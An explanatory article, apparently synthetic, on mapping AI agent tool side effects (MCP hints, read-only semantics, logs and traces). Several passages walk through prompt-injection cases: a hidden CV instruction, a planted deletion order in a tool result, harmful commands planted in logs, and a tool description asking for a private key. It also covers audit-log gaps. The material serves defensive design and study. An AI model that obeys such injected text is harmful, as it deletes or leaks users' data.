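# Mapping the side effects of an AI tool before deployment: logs, caches, notifications and shared state

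## What happens when an AI agent calls a tool

An AI agent is a large language model connected to a program that can act on the model's output. The model itself only produces text. To send an email, look up a customer or change a file, it writes a request to run a particular function, called a tool, and ordinary software runs that function. The tool returns a reply to the model, but running it often changes other things too. It may add a line to a log, keep a copy of an answer, alert a colleague, or alter a record that somebody else opens later. Mapping a tool's side effects means finding and recording these changes before anyone deploys the tool.

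Writers use different names for the parts of an agent system. Law, Li and colleagues (2026) note this in *Linking Event-sequence Data Claims to Analytic Provenance in Chatbots* and define the model as a stateless service that turns a prompt into a completion, and the agent as that model plus a "harness" built around it. The harness is the program that sends the model text, executes its tool calls and returns the results. A tool call is a structured request containing a function's name and arguments. A tool server is a program that offers tools to a harness and runs them. Other writers call the harness, or part of it, a "host", "client" or "interpreter".

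### The path of one call

Suppose a user asks an agent whether to take an umbrella in New York, and the agent has a tool named `get_weather`.

1. The harness sends the model the question and a list of the available tools. Each entry has a name, a description in ordinary language, and a schema, which is a formal statement of the arguments the tool accepts.
2. The model responds with a structured request: the name `get_weather` and the argument "New York" for the location. At this point nothing outside the conversation has changed. "The model never runs anything on its own," as Anthropic's *How tool use works* puts it.
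3. The harness reads the request and either runs it or first asks the user for permission. Most do not ask. Yao, Yang and colleagues (2026), in *When Neither Side Confirms*, examined the source code of 41 popular open-source applications and developer kits that run tool calls, and found that 32 have no approval step by default.
4. The harness passes the call to the tool server, which runs the tool's code. That code may do all its work locally, or it may contact an outside service, here a weather company. The outside service runs code of its own and may contact others in turn.
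5. The answer comes back through the tool server to the harness, which adds it to the conversation and runs the model again. The model now either writes its final answer or asks for another tool.

Each system that a call or its consequences pass through is a hop. The umbrella question has at least three: the harness, the tool server and the weather company. A longer task repeats the path many times. In Anthropic's interface, the harness is essentially a loop that keeps running tools as long as the model's responses end with a tool request. A single response can contain several requests.

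A tool's code sometimes runs on machines the agent's developer doesn't control. Anthropic runs web search, web fetching and code execution on its own infrastructure, and one request from a developer's application can trigger several searches before the application receives a response. The developer can see what ran, usually afterward, but can't step in between searches to record or stop anything.

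No single party to a call has all the information about it. The model receives the tool's description and its reply, but never its code. *Description-Code Inconsistency in Real-world MCP Servers* (Shi, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) calls this the "visibility gap". The tool server receives the arguments but generally not the conversation that led to them. The weather company receives a request for New York and may not know that a language model was involved. The harness handles every message, but the messages don't show what the server's code did between receiving the call and replying. Anyone who wants a list of everything that changed has to collect it from several places.

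### The Model Context Protocol

Harnesses and tool servers usually come from different developers, so they need a common format. The most widely used is the Model Context Protocol (MCP), an open standard that Anthropic introduced in 2024 (Granados, *MCP 2026 changes the rules*, 2026). MCP handles tools mainly through two messages (Model Context Protocol, *Tools*, 2026). A harness sends `tools/list` to learn what a server offers and `tools/call` to run a tool. In the standard's example of a weather lookup, the call carries the tool's name and the location, and the reply is a short text giving 72°F and partly cloudy skies. A server may also attach labels describing a tool's effects, but a harness must treat them as untrusted unless it trusts the server.

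In MCP, the harness is called a "host", and it runs one "client" for each server it connects to. Model Context Protocol's *Architecture* (2026) states as a design principle that the full conversation stays with the host and that servers cannot see into one another. A server can be a small program on the user's laptop or a remote service run by another company.

The standard is very widely used. When it released the current version, dated 28 July 2026, the Model Context Protocol (2026) project reported nearly half a billion monthly downloads of its main developer kits. Yao and colleagues counted 29,242 GitHub repositories in the official registry of servers. The next version is due on 30 March 2027, according to Model Context Protocol's *A More Predictable Release Cycle for MCP* (2026).

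The July version made the protocol stateless, meaning that each request carries everything the server needs to interpret it and the server keeps no session open between requests. Tools can still keep state between calls. The specification describes a shopping server whose `create_basket` tool returns an identifier, which the model passes back with each later call. The server stores the basket's contents under that identifier and still has them after the conversation ends.

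### Effects that a description mentions and effects that it leaves out

A side effect is any change a tool call causes outside the reply it returns, whether or not anyone intended it. Law and colleagues contrast a tool that adds two numbers, which has no side effects, with a coding agent's tool that writes a file and commits it to a GitHub repository. For many tools, including the second one, the side effect is the purpose of the call.

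Problems arise when a tool call also does something nobody asked for. *Towards Practically-Secure Tools for AI Agents* (Adam, Lu and colleagues, 2026) gives a short example. A tool named `write_file` takes a path and some content, and is described as writing the content to the file at that path. The code does this, but first it sends a metrics module a small record containing the tool's name and the length of the content. Both actions are side effects, but the description mentions only the intended one, writing the file.

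The example code sends the metric before it writes the file, so if the write fails, for instance because the folder doesn't exist, the model gets an error even though the record has already gone out. An error message therefore doesn't prove that nothing happened. The code also opens the file in a Python mode that erases its existing contents. The word "writes" describes this only loosely, and a model that thought the tool added text to a file would destroy the old contents. The code doesn't show where the metrics module sends its records, which could be a file on the same machine or a company in another country.

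Adam and colleagues say that such a metric may leak private data when somebody is editing a closed-source project. A single tool name and a length reveal very little, so the stronger objection is probably that neither the user nor the model could decide whether to send them. An accurate tool description would have allowed a harness to avoid the tool for sensitive work.

Adam and colleagues wrote the example to illustrate a point, so it doesn't show how often this happens. To measure that, Shi and colleagues compared descriptions with code for 19,200 tools on 2,214 real MCP servers. They write $\Psi_{act}$ for the set of effects that the code produces and $\Psi_{claim}$ for the set that the description discloses. A tool has undeclared side effects when $\Psi_{act} \nsubseteq \Psi_{claim}$, meaning that at least one real effect is missing from the description. A description that warns of an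 effect that never occurs still passes this test. They found some inconsistency in 9.93% of the tools, but most of these cases were other mismatches, chiefly descriptions that promised features the code lacked. The share with undeclared side effects must therefore be well below 10%.

Shi and colleagues also discuss a weather tool whose description mentions only the lookup. Besides doing the lookup, its code saves the city in a usage history, updates the user's profile and reports the query in an analytics event. The developer may have wanted to offer better recommendations later, but the user doesn't know that the tool is storing a history of the places they ask about.

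### Channels, surfaces and maps

Side effects spread by four routes, or channels, and a plain case of each is enough for now.

- Logs: a tool looks up a customer's account, and the tool server adds a line to a file with the time and the customer's name.
- Caches: a currency tool fetches the exchange rate at nine o'clock, keeps it, and gives the same figure to everyone who asks before noon.
- Notifications and events: a calendar tool adds a meeting, and the calendar service emails the six people invited.
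- Shared state: a warehouse tool lowers a stock count from 12 to 11, and the next agent to check the stock gets 11.

One call can use several channels at once, and the channels are not sharply distinct. The weather tool's usage history looks like a log, but it serves as shared state if the tool later uses it to make recommendations.

A tool's side-effect surface is the set of all side effects that calls to it can cause, in every system the calls reach. For example, `write_file` might create a harmless text file or overwrite a configuration file, depending on the path it receives, and both effects belong to its surface. An effect map is the written record of that surface. For each effect, it lists the data involved, who or what can read that data, how long the data lasts, whether anyone can reverse the change, and what evidence there is that the effect occurs.

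Adam and colleagues use "effect" more broadly, for any interaction between a tool and the world, including reading a file. They have good reason to, because a tool may read a secret in one step and send it over the network in another. In an effect map, a read appears as the source of the data in a later effect, since reading alone need not change anything.

The effect map combines techniques that software engineers, security specialists and agent researchers developed separately and for different purposes. It is not an established standard, and nobody has tested the combination as a whole.

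In reinforcement learning, where a program learns from rewards, "side effects" has an older meaning. *Concrete Problems in AI Safety* (2016) gives the example of a robot that knocks over a vase while moving a box across a room. *Challenges for Using Impact Regularizers to Avoid Negative Side Effects* (Lindner, Matoba and Meulemans, 2021) reviews attempts to prevent such damage by adding a penalty for impact to the reward. A tool's side effects come from ordinary code rather than from how the agent pursues its goal, and they can occur even when the model makes the right tool call.

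### When a result contains instructions

The last step of the path, when the tool's result enters the conversation, also gives attackers a way in. In prompt injection, an attacker places text in material that a model reads so that the model treats it as instructions. *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, written by David C for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre in December 2025, gives the example of a recruiter who uses a model to score job applications. One candidate uses a hidden sentence in a CV to tell the model to ignore its instructions and approve the candidate for an interview.

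This weakness comes from how language models process text. A model predicts the next piece of text from all the text so far, and nothing in that process marks which passages are commands and which are data. Databases once had a similar flaw, which programmers fixed by passing commands and data separately. David C doubts that anyone will find an equally complete fix for language models. He advises designers to assume that an attacker who gets text into a model's input may be able to use every tool the model has.

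Yao and colleagues tested this by building a small notes server and having agents list the notes and delete one called "old draft". The researchers had planted an instruction in the returned list to delete "tax records 2025" as well. Of five low-cost models, one never attempted the second deletion. The other four carried it out in 479 of 960 runs, ranging from 10 of 240 for one model to 215 of 240 for another. When the server had no confirmation step, all 180 attempted deletions succeeded, so the only protection was the model not attempting the deletion. Because the test used low-cost models and a toy server, its figures should not be applied to the strongest current systems. Recorded incidents of prompt injection also remain relatively few, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *Prompt Injection Remains Biggest LLM Risk, Despite Limited Incidents*. The security foundation OWASP nevertheless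 put prompt injection at the top of its August 2026 list of risks for applications built on language models, for the third year running.

Prompt injection makes side effects matter in a way they would not in older software. Text that one call writes to a log or database record can later reach a model as the result of another call. An effect map therefore has to include models among the possible readers of each piece of data.

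### A tool that opens tickets

Suppose a company gives its coding agent a tool called `create_ticket(title, body, assignee)`, an invented example that resembles many real tools. It opens a ticket in the company's issue tracker, where staff record faults and requests and follow them until someone closes them. The title is a single line, the body is free text of any length, and the assignee is the employee who should handle the ticket.

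A developer tells the agent that the checkout page crashes when the basket is empty and asks it to report the fault to Maria, who looks after that page. The model writes a title and a description of the crash and names Maria as assignee. The harness sends the call to the tool server, which passes it to the tracker over the network. The model gets back only "Created ticket SHOP-482." The tool's description is only "Opens a ticket in the issue tracker." The tracker is another company's product, and other teams use it too, some through their own agents.

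## What "read-only" means and what tools declare about themselves

Suppose the server behind `create_ticket` also offers `get_ticket(id)`, which returns the text of a ticket. Each time an agent calls it, the tracker probably adds a line to an access log, and it may put the ticket on somebody's "recently viewed" list. Most people would call this tool read-only and let an agent use it freely, but whether it is read-only depends on which changes count.

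### Safe requests on the web

Web engineers had to settle this question long before agents existed, because browsers and search engines fetch huge numbers of pages without anyone reviewing each request. In HTTP, the protocol they use, every request has a method, such as GET to fetch something or DELETE to remove it. *HTTP Semantics* (Fielding, 2022), the web standard also known as RFC 9110, calls a method "safe" if its defined meaning is "essentially read-only". The client, the program making the request, neither asks for nor expects a change of state on the server. Reasonable use of a safe method should also cause no harm, loss of property or unusual burden. GET and three less familiar methods are safe.

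The definition concerns what the client asks for, so a server may still do something that isn't entirely read-only, or is even harmful, when it answers a safe request. Fielding gives the example of an access log. Most servers add a line to one after every response, and the request still counts as safe even though the log might fill the disk and crash the server. Clicking on an advertisement also sends a safe request, and often charges the advertiser's account.

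Fielding reasons that the client isn't accountable for the extra behavior because it didn't request it. Connected: Internet Encyclopedia's *Safe Methods* reproduces the older HTTP/1.0 wording, which gives the same reason for not holding the user accountable and acknowledges that nobody can guarantee a GET request without side effects. Kyle Rose, writing on the HTTP working group's mailing list, suggests that the client has to judge safety alone because it can't know what the server is doing. Developers mapping their own tool server are better placed because they can read its code.

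HTTP's definition of a safe method concerns who is responsible for side effects. An effect map has to record what happens regardless of who is responsible, so it must include both the log line and the advertising charge.

The label is meant to let programs make requests unattended. Search engines crawl the web and browsers fetch pages in advance on the assumption that a GET request won't break anything. Fielding points out that if a site puts an action in an address, as in `page?do=delete`, a program that follows every link to build a search index will delete the pages. The standard makes the site's owner responsible for blocking such actions when they are requested through a safe method.

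### Lookups that change something

A credit-check tool might cost $2 per query. This resembles Fielding's advertisement, except that the agent's own company pays and knows it will. One query is probably reasonable use, but an agent stuck in a loop that makes 5,000 queries overnight spends $10,000. Each call is identical, so the harm comes entirely from the number of calls, which a yes-or-no label on the tool can't express.

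A less obvious case is an agent that opens 40 unread emails to summarize them, which causes the mail service to mark each one as read. By Fielding's test this is safe, because the agent asked only for the text. But many people use unread marks as a to-do list, and an owner who does this can no longer tell which messages need an answer. Someone could restore the marks if the agent kept a list of what it opened. If the service also sends read receipts, the senders learn that somebody opened their messages, and nobody can undo that.

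Some links work only once, such as a link to a password that the server destroys after showing it. If a GET request uses up the link, the site has made the same mistake as with `page?do=delete`, and a program that checks links for viruses may use it up before the recipient clicks. The call is still idempotent, meaning that making it twice leaves the same state as making it once. Fielding notes that a client can safely repeat idempotent requests after a lost connection, though the response might differ. In this case, a harness that loses the first reply and tries again gets an error instead of the password, which the server has already destroyed.

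These cases are easier to handle if "read-only" always means read-only with respect to something. Let $W(c)$ be the set of resources that a call $c$ changes, and let $P$ be the set of resources that somebody wants to protect. Then $c$ is read-only with respect to $P$ when

$$W(c) \cap P = \varnothing.$$

Opening an email is read-only with respect to message text but not unread marks. `get_ticket` is read-only with respect to tickets but not the access log. If $P$ contains everything, hardly any tool that uses a network will be read-only. For a tool to be read-only, the condition must hold for every call it accepts. A `run_query` tool that takes any database command isn't read-only, even if agents mostly use it to look things up.

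No standard contains this definition. It is a convenience for writing effect maps, useful mainly because the writer must name $P$.

### The four hints in MCP

Since March 2025, the Model Context Protocol (MCP) has let a server attach four yes-or-no labels to each tool. The MCP project calls them hints, and its review of them gives an example of how a harness might use each one.

| Hint | What the server claims by setting it to true | Value if missing | What a harness might do when it is true |
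|---|---|---|---|
| `readOnlyHint` | The tool doesn't modify its environment | false | Skip the confirmation |
| `destructiveHint` | Its changes may destroy something, rather than only add | true | Show a warning first |
| `idempotentHint` | Repeating a call with the same arguments is safe | false | Retry after a failure |
| `openWorldHint` | It deals with outside entities, not a closed domain | true | Check the output for untrusted content |

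The defaults are cautious. If a server attaches no labels to `create_ticket`, a harness should assume that the tool can change and destroy things, that repeating a call is unsafe, and that the tool reaches outside systems. Most of these assumptions are correct for this tool. But the project advises developers to set `destructiveHint` to false for operations that only add something, which seems to include opening a ticket.

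Even an honest developer could have trouble setting `readOnlyHint`, because it isn't obvious whether a log is part of the tool's "environment". One whose weather tool keeps a history of searches might label the tool read-only. The hint also applies to the whole tool rather than to each call, so `run_query` has the same label whether it looks up an address or erases the customer table.

*The Safe Response Header Field* (Holtman, 1998) proposed an earlier label of this kind, a way for web servers to declare that repeating a request was safe. Browsers could then have skipped the dialog box that asks whether to send a form again. The proposal began as experimental but didn't last, and its status is now "historic".

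MCP's current revision leaves the four hints unchanged, according to the project's list of changes for July (Model Context Protocol, 2026). In early 2026 the project counted five open proposals for new annotations or closely related features, including a `secretHint` and an `unsafeOutputHint`. An interest group with members from Microsoft, OpenAI, AWS, Cloudflare and Anthropic, among others, planned to discuss whether replies should carry annotations too, and whether software should work out some annotations at the time of the call, which would help with `run_query`. Any change has to wait for a later revision, and under the project's new release schedule a proposal that isn't ready moves to the next release instead of delaying the current one.

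### Effect types and footprints

Kovalenko and Redchych (2026), in *Small Agents Should Know What Their Tools Do*, built a simulated office and online shop called EffectWorld, in which every tool declares more than MCP's hints can express. Each tool has one of four effect types:

- A pure tool computes its result from its arguments alone, such as turning "next Friday" into a date.
- A read tool looks at the state of the world without changing it, such as listing emails.
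- A write tool makes a change that someone can correct later, such as moving a meeting.
- A destructive tool makes a change that nobody can take back, because it deletes data, reaches other people or moves money.

In EffectWorld, sending an email counts as destructive. It deletes nothing and merely adds to the mailbox, but the sender can't take back what other people have already seen. Kovalenko and Redchych classify actions by their consequences rather than their mechanism, whereas MCP contrasts "destructive" with "additive". A developer could therefore honestly set `destructiveHint` to false on an email tool that EffectWorld would class as destructive.

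If the tracker emails Maria about her new ticket, the `create_ticket` call reaches another person and is destructive in EffectWorld's sense; otherwise it is an ordinary write. The tool's type may therefore depend on a notification setting in another company's product, which appears in neither the tool's code nor its description. The credit-check tool is also hard to classify, because it looks like a read but moves money, and a tool has only one type.

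EffectWorld declares idempotence separately, because it doesn't follow from the type. Canceling an order is destructive but idempotent. Creating a calendar event is only a write, yet doing it twice leaves two events.

Each tool also has a footprint, which consists of the resources that a call reads and the resources that it writes. These are patterns filled in from the call's arguments. `update_event` reads and writes `event:{event_id}`, meaning the one event named in the call, while `find_events` reads `event:*`, meaning all of them. If an argument isn't known yet, the pattern covers everything it could refer to. The idea comes from compilers, which use similar declarations to decide which parts of a program they can safely rearrange. With $R$ for the resources read and $W$ for those written, two calls $a$ and $b$ can run in either order if

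$$W(a) \cap \big(R(b) \cup W(b)\big) = \varnothing \quad \text{and} \quad W(b) \cap R(a) = \varnothing.$$

Two calls can run in either order if neither writes anything that the other reads or writes. For example, an agent can move two different meetings in either order. But if it lists all the meetings and moves one of them, the list will depend on which call happens first.

Footprints let a program check an agent's behavior without human judges. The program replays the recorded calls and tests three rules: the user confirmed every destructive call, the agent read whatever it was about to change, and the agent never repeated a write that isn't idempotent. This works only if the declarations are true. Kovalenko and Redchych could make sure they were, because they wrote both the tools and the declarations. A production tool depends on libraries and outside services that its developer may know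 little about, and the developer is likely to miss the parts of a footprint that matter most to an effect map.

### What small models learned about asking first

Kovalenko and Redchych also trained models on examples of good behavior in the simulated office, including asking before destructive calls. Their main model was a version of Qwen3 with 4 billion parameters, which is small by current standards. It made 94 unconfirmed destructive calls in 498 office tasks before training and none after.

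They then moved the model to the online shop, whose 17 tools it had never seen. Across 547 tasks, the untrained model made 7 unconfirmed destructive calls. The trained version they used as their reference made 24, although it completed more of the tasks (83%, up from 74%). On tasks that involved buying an item, the trained versions paid without asking in 13 to 19 of 28 cases. The model had apparently learned to ask before using particular office tools, and the habit didn't carry over to tools with new names.

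One possible explanation was that the model had seen only each tool's name, description and parameters, not the effect declarations. Kovalenko and Redchych therefore trained another version with the effect type and idempotence written into the descriptions. They also renamed the office tools in a third of the office examples so that the model couldn't rely on names. Unconfirmed destructive calls fell from 24 to 19, which was not a statistically significant improvement and was still far above the untrained model's 7. However, the share of purchases that the model made only after confirmation rose from 32% to 50%.

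It's hard to say how much of this was due to the labels, since the tool names changed at the same time. The main comparison also doesn't include an untrained model given the labels, so it can't show whether the labels alone would help a model that already tends to ask. Training also made three other small models less cautious in the shop, where their unconfirmed destructive calls rose from 1, 2 and 2 to 45, 6 and 39. These increases are weaker evidence than they look, because the models completed only 8% to 14% of the shop tasks before training and so had fewer opportunities to spend money without permission. None of the models had more than 4 billion parameters, and a frontier model might make much better use of the same labels.

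The count also measures only whether the agent asked for confirmation. The simulated user approves every proposal it recognizes, even one to cancel the wrong order, and the program still records the call as confirmed. A real user might catch the mistake or click "yes" out of habit.

A harness can act on labels more reliably than these models did, because it can refuse to run a destructive call until the user confirms it. This works only if the tools are labeled correctly.

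### What servers declare in practice

Trofimov and Novikov (2026), in *When Tool Calls Succeed but Workflows Fail*, measured how often MCP servers supply the four hints. They copied the official registry on 27 July 2026, when it listed 18,688 distinct servers. They left out about half because those had no remote address, and examining them would have meant running their code. They requested tool lists from the remaining 9,234. Of these, 4,838 returned at least one tool, giving 98,291 tools in total, and nearly all the rest failed to connect. The results therefore describe remote servers that anyone could reach that day, and may not hold for programs that people install on their own computers.

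At least one hint appeared on 74.0% of the tools, and all four appeared on 61.7%. But a single publisher, listed as `io.github.pipeworx-io`, accounted for 44,227 tools, or 45.0% of the total, and every one of them had all four hints. Without that publisher, the shares fall to 52.8% and 30.3%. Most of the publisher's tools also had the same combination of values. A hint can evidently come from a template, so its presence is weak evidence that a developer thought about the particular tool.

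`destructiveHint` was present on 65.8% of tools, but it has no meaning on a tool also marked read-only. Once Trofimov and Novikov excluded those, it applied to only 12.9% of tools, and 3.1% were marked destructive. Leaving out the large publisher changes these figures little, to 11.7% and 3.2%. For the great majority of tools, a harness designed to warn users about destructive calls therefore has either a read-only label or no explicit information to use.

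Read-only declarations were much more common. At least 52.8% of the tools were declared read-only, or at least 26.0% excluding the large publisher. These figures count only tools that also set `destructiveHint`, so the full shares may be higher. The read-only hint is the one that allows a harness to skip confirmation, and it is unclear how many of these declarations are true. Trofimov and Novikov never called a tool, and they note that their census covers declarations, not behavior. Shi and colleagues found few undeclared side effects, which is mildly reassuring, but they tested descriptions, not hints.

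Even accurate labels would leave out a lot. Trofimov and Novikov, whose paper mainly catalogs what goes wrong when calls fail, repeat or overlap, note that no hint specifies how a harness can check whether an earlier call succeeded or how to reverse it. Unlike a footprint, the hints also don't identify which resources a tool touches.

### Whether a read-only call can run unattended

The intuitive argument for skipping confirmation is that a read-only tool changes nothing that matters, so calls to it need no review and may run unattended.

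A tool accurately labelled read-only may still change something that matters. Suppose an agent has a read-only tool called `fetch_page(url)`, and a prompt injection causes the model to open an address on the attacker's website that contains a customer's name. The tool sends an ordinary GET request, which leaves the page unchanged, but the attacker's server records the address, including the name, in its access log. HTTP treats that log entry as incidental, but here it is the purpose of the attack. Fielding warns that a GET request can put sensitive data into an address where it doesn't belong. Of the four hints, only `openWorldHint` would give a harness any reason for concern.

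Even a call that changes nothing might need review, because a person may want to decide whether the agent should see the data at all. The reply can also affect what the agent does next. In the test by Yao and colleagues, the planted instruction arrived through a tool that only listed notes. A harmless search tool can also become part of a data leak if the agent has another tool that sends messages.

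A check after the call makes more sense than having someone approve every read beforehand. An approver would see only the request, so they couldn't spot an instruction hidden in the reply, and they would probably stop paying attention after the first few dozen requests. The Model Context Protocol project suggests that a harness could treat a session as tainted once a tool has brought in untrusted data, and require more approvals from then on.

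Letting calls run unattended creates another problem, because they can run in large numbers. Fielding's definition excludes "unusual burden", and an agent in a loop can easily create one, as with the credit checks.

A narrower version of the argument seems sound. A call may run unattended if something other than the tool's own label prevents it from changing the protected resources, its arguments can't carry private data to outsiders, the harness treats its reply as untrusted, and the number of calls is limited. `get_ticket` could meet these conditions, and so could `fetch_page` if the harness restricted it to a short list of websites. The condition about private data is very hard for a general web-browsing tool to meet.

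### The dispute over hints that nobody can trust

The designers of MCP argued about this during the review, before they adopted the hints. Justin Spahr-Summers, one of MCP's creators, agreed that the information would be very useful if it were trustworthy, but wondered what a client could do with a flag it couldn't trust. Basil Hosmer argued that clients should ignore all annotations from untrusted servers, especially those about how a tool behaves. A malicious server can label a tool read-only even if the tool deletes the user's files. The designers compromised by calling everything a hint, telling clients to distrust hints by default, and letting each client decide how much weight to give them.

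There is a reasonable case for keeping these hints. A company that runs its own tool servers has reason to trust their hints and can base rules on them, such as blocking tools that reach the outside world once a session has touched private data. A system that enforces such rules can also check the hints against other information, so they don't have to be perfect. If an unknown server wrongly labels its tool destructive, the user only sees an unnecessary dialog box, whereas a false read-only label removes a safeguard. A harness can therefore accept warnings from any server but reassurances only from servers it trusts.

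That policy depends on harnesses distinguishing between servers, but the project's review found that most trust every installed server. The review also found that no MCP client displayed the hints in its approval prompts.

The project answers Spahr-Summers's question by separating hints from contracts. If relying on a false label would be dangerous, the guarantee has to come from something that enforces it, such as access permissions, network controls or a sandbox (a restricted environment that limits what a program can reach). Hints can still improve the interface and inform decisions where a mistake is tolerable. This seems right, and it means that an effect map should treat `readOnlyHint` as evidence of what the developer claims rather than evidence that the tool has no effects.

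For `get_ticket`, the company could give the tool server a tracker account that can only view tickets. A bug or a dishonest update then couldn't edit or delete tickets through that account. The server could still copy a ticket's text into its own logs or send it elsewhere. If the company runs the server itself, it can block the server's outgoing connections to everything except the tracker. If another company runs it, the only protection left is to limit which tickets the account can view.

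## Logs: what is recorded, who reads it and how long it lasts

A tool server that can only view tickets can still copy their text into a log, and so can most of the other systems a call passes through. Suppose the developer who reported the checkout crash pasted in an error message containing a customer's email address, and the model copied the message into the ticket's body. The address is now in the tracker, as the developer would expect, but it may also be in several logs the developer doesn't know about.

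### Four kinds of record

People use "log" loosely for several kinds of record with different purposes and readers.

| Record | What it holds | Who reads it, and why | Example for `create_ticket` |
|---|---|---|---|
| Log | Separate entries, each describing one event and its time | Developers, to find out why something failed | 14:02, created SHOP-482 |
| Trace | Linked, timed records of the steps in one task, often across several systems | Developers, to find the slow or faulty step | Model 2.1 seconds, tool 0.4 seconds |
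| Metric | Numbers added up over many calls | Operators, to watch load and cost | 212 tickets today, 3 failures |
| Audit record | Who did what to which item, and with whose permission | Auditors and investigators, to establish responsibility | The coding agent opened SHOP-482 for a named developer |

Engineers call each step in a trace a span. Many teams keep only a sample of their traces, perhaps one in ten. That is enough to find a slow step but not for an audit, which needs a complete record that is hard to alter. *Auditable Agents* (Nian, Yuan and colleagues, 2026) grades a record's protection against alteration on four levels, from a record that anyone can edit unnoticed to one with a digital signature that outsiders can check. Outsiders can use the signature to confirm that nobody changed the entries, but not to detect an entry that the system never wrote.

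### Where copies of a call end up

A single call to `create_ticket` could leave copies of its arguments in six places.

- Harness trace: the harness handles the whole conversation, so its trace can include the developer's messages as well as the ticket.
- Gateway: companies with many agents often place a program between their harnesses and tool servers to control and record calls. Its log can collect arguments from every team in one place.
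- Tool server: the tool's own code may log the arguments, or a library it uses may log every outgoing request.
- Outside service: the tracker probably keeps an access log and a history of edits to each ticket. Its owner decides how long they last.
- Error tracker: when a call crashes, the program may send a report to a service that collects errors, often run by another company. The report can include the data the program was handling, so a failed call sometimes leaves more text behind than a successful one.
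- Backup: this may copy any of the others, and removing a single entry from it is usually impractical.

### What OpenTelemetry captures by default

OpenTelemetry is a widely used open standard for collecting logs, traces and metrics. Its *Semantic conventions for generative client AI spans* specifies what a trace should contain when a program uses a language model. For a tool call, it recommends recording the tool's name and description and the call's identifier. The call's arguments and result, the model's instructions, and the messages the model receives and writes are all "opt-in", so a library should leave them out unless a developer asks for them. By default, a trace shows that an agent called `create_ticket`, how long the call took and whether it failed, but omits the arguments, such as the customer's email address.

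Leaving argument capture off doesn't keep a ticket's text out of the trace if message capture is on, because the messages contain the tool calls. The trace can also repeat the text, because the harness sends the model the conversation so far with each call. In OpenTelemetry's *LLM call examples*, a weather question takes two model calls, and the second one's input contains the question, the tool call and the result. If an agent opens a ticket in the first of ten model calls, the trace can contain the ticket's body ten times, once as output and nine times as input.

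For production systems with sensitive data, OpenTelemetry recommends keeping the content in a separate store and putting only a reference to it in the trace. The code that uploads the content is supposed to work independently of the opt-in settings, so someone who checks only those settings could conclude that the company keeps no content when it keeps all of it elsewhere.

The conventions also have the status "Development", so they may still change, and according to OpenTelemetry's *Moved* they now have their own repository. Existing libraries should keep producing the older format until a developer opts in to the new one. An effect map should therefore record what the installed version captures. The conventions do not prevent a tool's own code from writing the tool's arguments to a file.

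### Secrets copied into logs

Developers often print a program's internal values to the screen while testing it, and sometimes they forget to remove the code that does this. This does little harm on a laptop, but a harness often captures whatever a tool prints and passes it to the model, so a printed password enters the conversation and every record of it.

*How Your Credentials Are Leaked by LLM Agent Skills* (Chen, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) measured how often this happens with credentials, such as passwords and access keys, in skills, which are packages of written instructions and code that people install to extend an agent. The researchers sampled 17,022 of the 170,226 skills on one marketplace, searched them for risky handling of credentials and found 3,156 candidates. They ran each candidate in a sandbox with fake credentials, three times normally and three times with a prompt injection.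 Three of the researchers then reviewed the 1,427 skills that had behaved suspiciously.

Chen and colleagues found 520 skills that leaked credentials, 83 of them malicious. The other 437 had 1,371 faults, which they attribute to carelessness. Of these, 1,007 (73.5%) exposed credentials through output such as debugging messages. These faults affected 352 skills, or about 2% of the sample. One skill for Google Workspace printed the tokens that give access to the user's account.

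The study covers one marketplace and doesn't weight skills by how often people use them, so the share of calls that leak a secret could be very different from the share of skills that do. It also counts only credentials, many of which have a recognizable format. A customer's name or medical complaint doesn't, so personal data in logs is harder to measure and probably harder to remove.

Even a carefully written tool can receive a secret in an argument. CrowdStrike's *How Agentic Tool Chain Attacks Threaten AI Agent Security* (2026) describes a tool that adds two numbers. The tool's description contains a hidden instruction for the model to read a private key and pass it as a "sidenote". The tool adds correctly, but the key goes into the logs and on to the tool server. This is an illustration, not a reported incident, but any log that stores arguments would record the key.

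### Log text that another agent reads as instructions

Error messages often quote the input that caused the error, so anyone who can trigger an error can often write text into a log. If a company later asks an agent to investigate the fault, that text reaches a model.

*LogJack* (Shah, 2026) tested eight models as assistants for debugging cloud systems. Shah placed 32 harmful commands in realistic logs and error reports, some of them disguised as steps from a company's repair manual. Each model had 160 trials, five for each command, and the test harness intercepted the commands instead of running them. When the models were free to investigate and fix problems, the share of trials in which a model's first dangerous command matched the planted one word for word ranged from 0% for Claude Sonnet 4.6 to 86.2% for Llama 3.3 70B. When Shah told the models to report their findings and fix nothing,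 Llama's share fell to 30.0% and every other model's was below 2%.

Filters for prompt injection were little help. Microsoft's caught 1 of the 32 planted commands and Google's caught none, although both caught the same commands when given them without the surrounding log text. Some models issued dangerous commands even when nothing had been planted in the logs. Llama did so in 22 of 50 trials and Claude Opus 4.6 in 9. Some of those logs described incidents that staff had already resolved, including the repair steps they took. None of the eight models is among the strongest available now, so the rates are out of date, but attackers can still reach a model through the logs it reads.

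OpenClaw, an open-source personal assistant, let anyone who could connect to it write roughly 14,800 characters into its log without signing in, according to Eye Security's *Log Poisoning in OpenClaw* (2026). When the researchers planted instructions there and asked the agent to debug a problem, it warned the user and refused to follow them. The developers have since fixed the flaw. The security company Tenet had more success with fake reports sent to Sentry, a popular error tracker. Hackread's *Agentjacking* reports that Tenet found 2,388 organizations with exposed Sentry reporting addresses, and that agents at more than 100 companies ran its test code.

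*Cypress Failures Are Untrusted Input to the AI Agent Triaging Them* (Mikhalev, 2026) describes a smaller test, in which a customer's note ended up in the error message from a failed software test. One of three open models acted on the note in 156 of 165 attempts. For each log, an effect map should therefore record who can write text into it, which agents read it and what tools those agents have. Limiting a log-reading agent to tools that can't change anything would have stopped the commands in Shah's test, whichever model it used.

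### Records that are missing when somebody needs them

Microsoft's documentation for Copilot Studio, its product for building agents, lists the administrative actions that the product logs. Datadog's *Uncovering agent logging gaps in Copilot Studio* (2026) found that four of these actions left no record from at least 29 August to 25 September 2025. They included removing an agent's sign-in requirement and turning off the log of its conversations. An attacker with editing rights could have done both, published the agent and extracted its data anonymously, leaving no record of the changes or the conversations. Microsoft had fixed all four by October, but in later tests two were again recorded only sometimes or not at all. In March 2026 Microsoft said it couldn't reproduce the problem. The AI Incident Database's *Incident 1218* describes a similar gap in Microsoft 365 Copilot, which reportedly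 let users read files without creating an audit entry.

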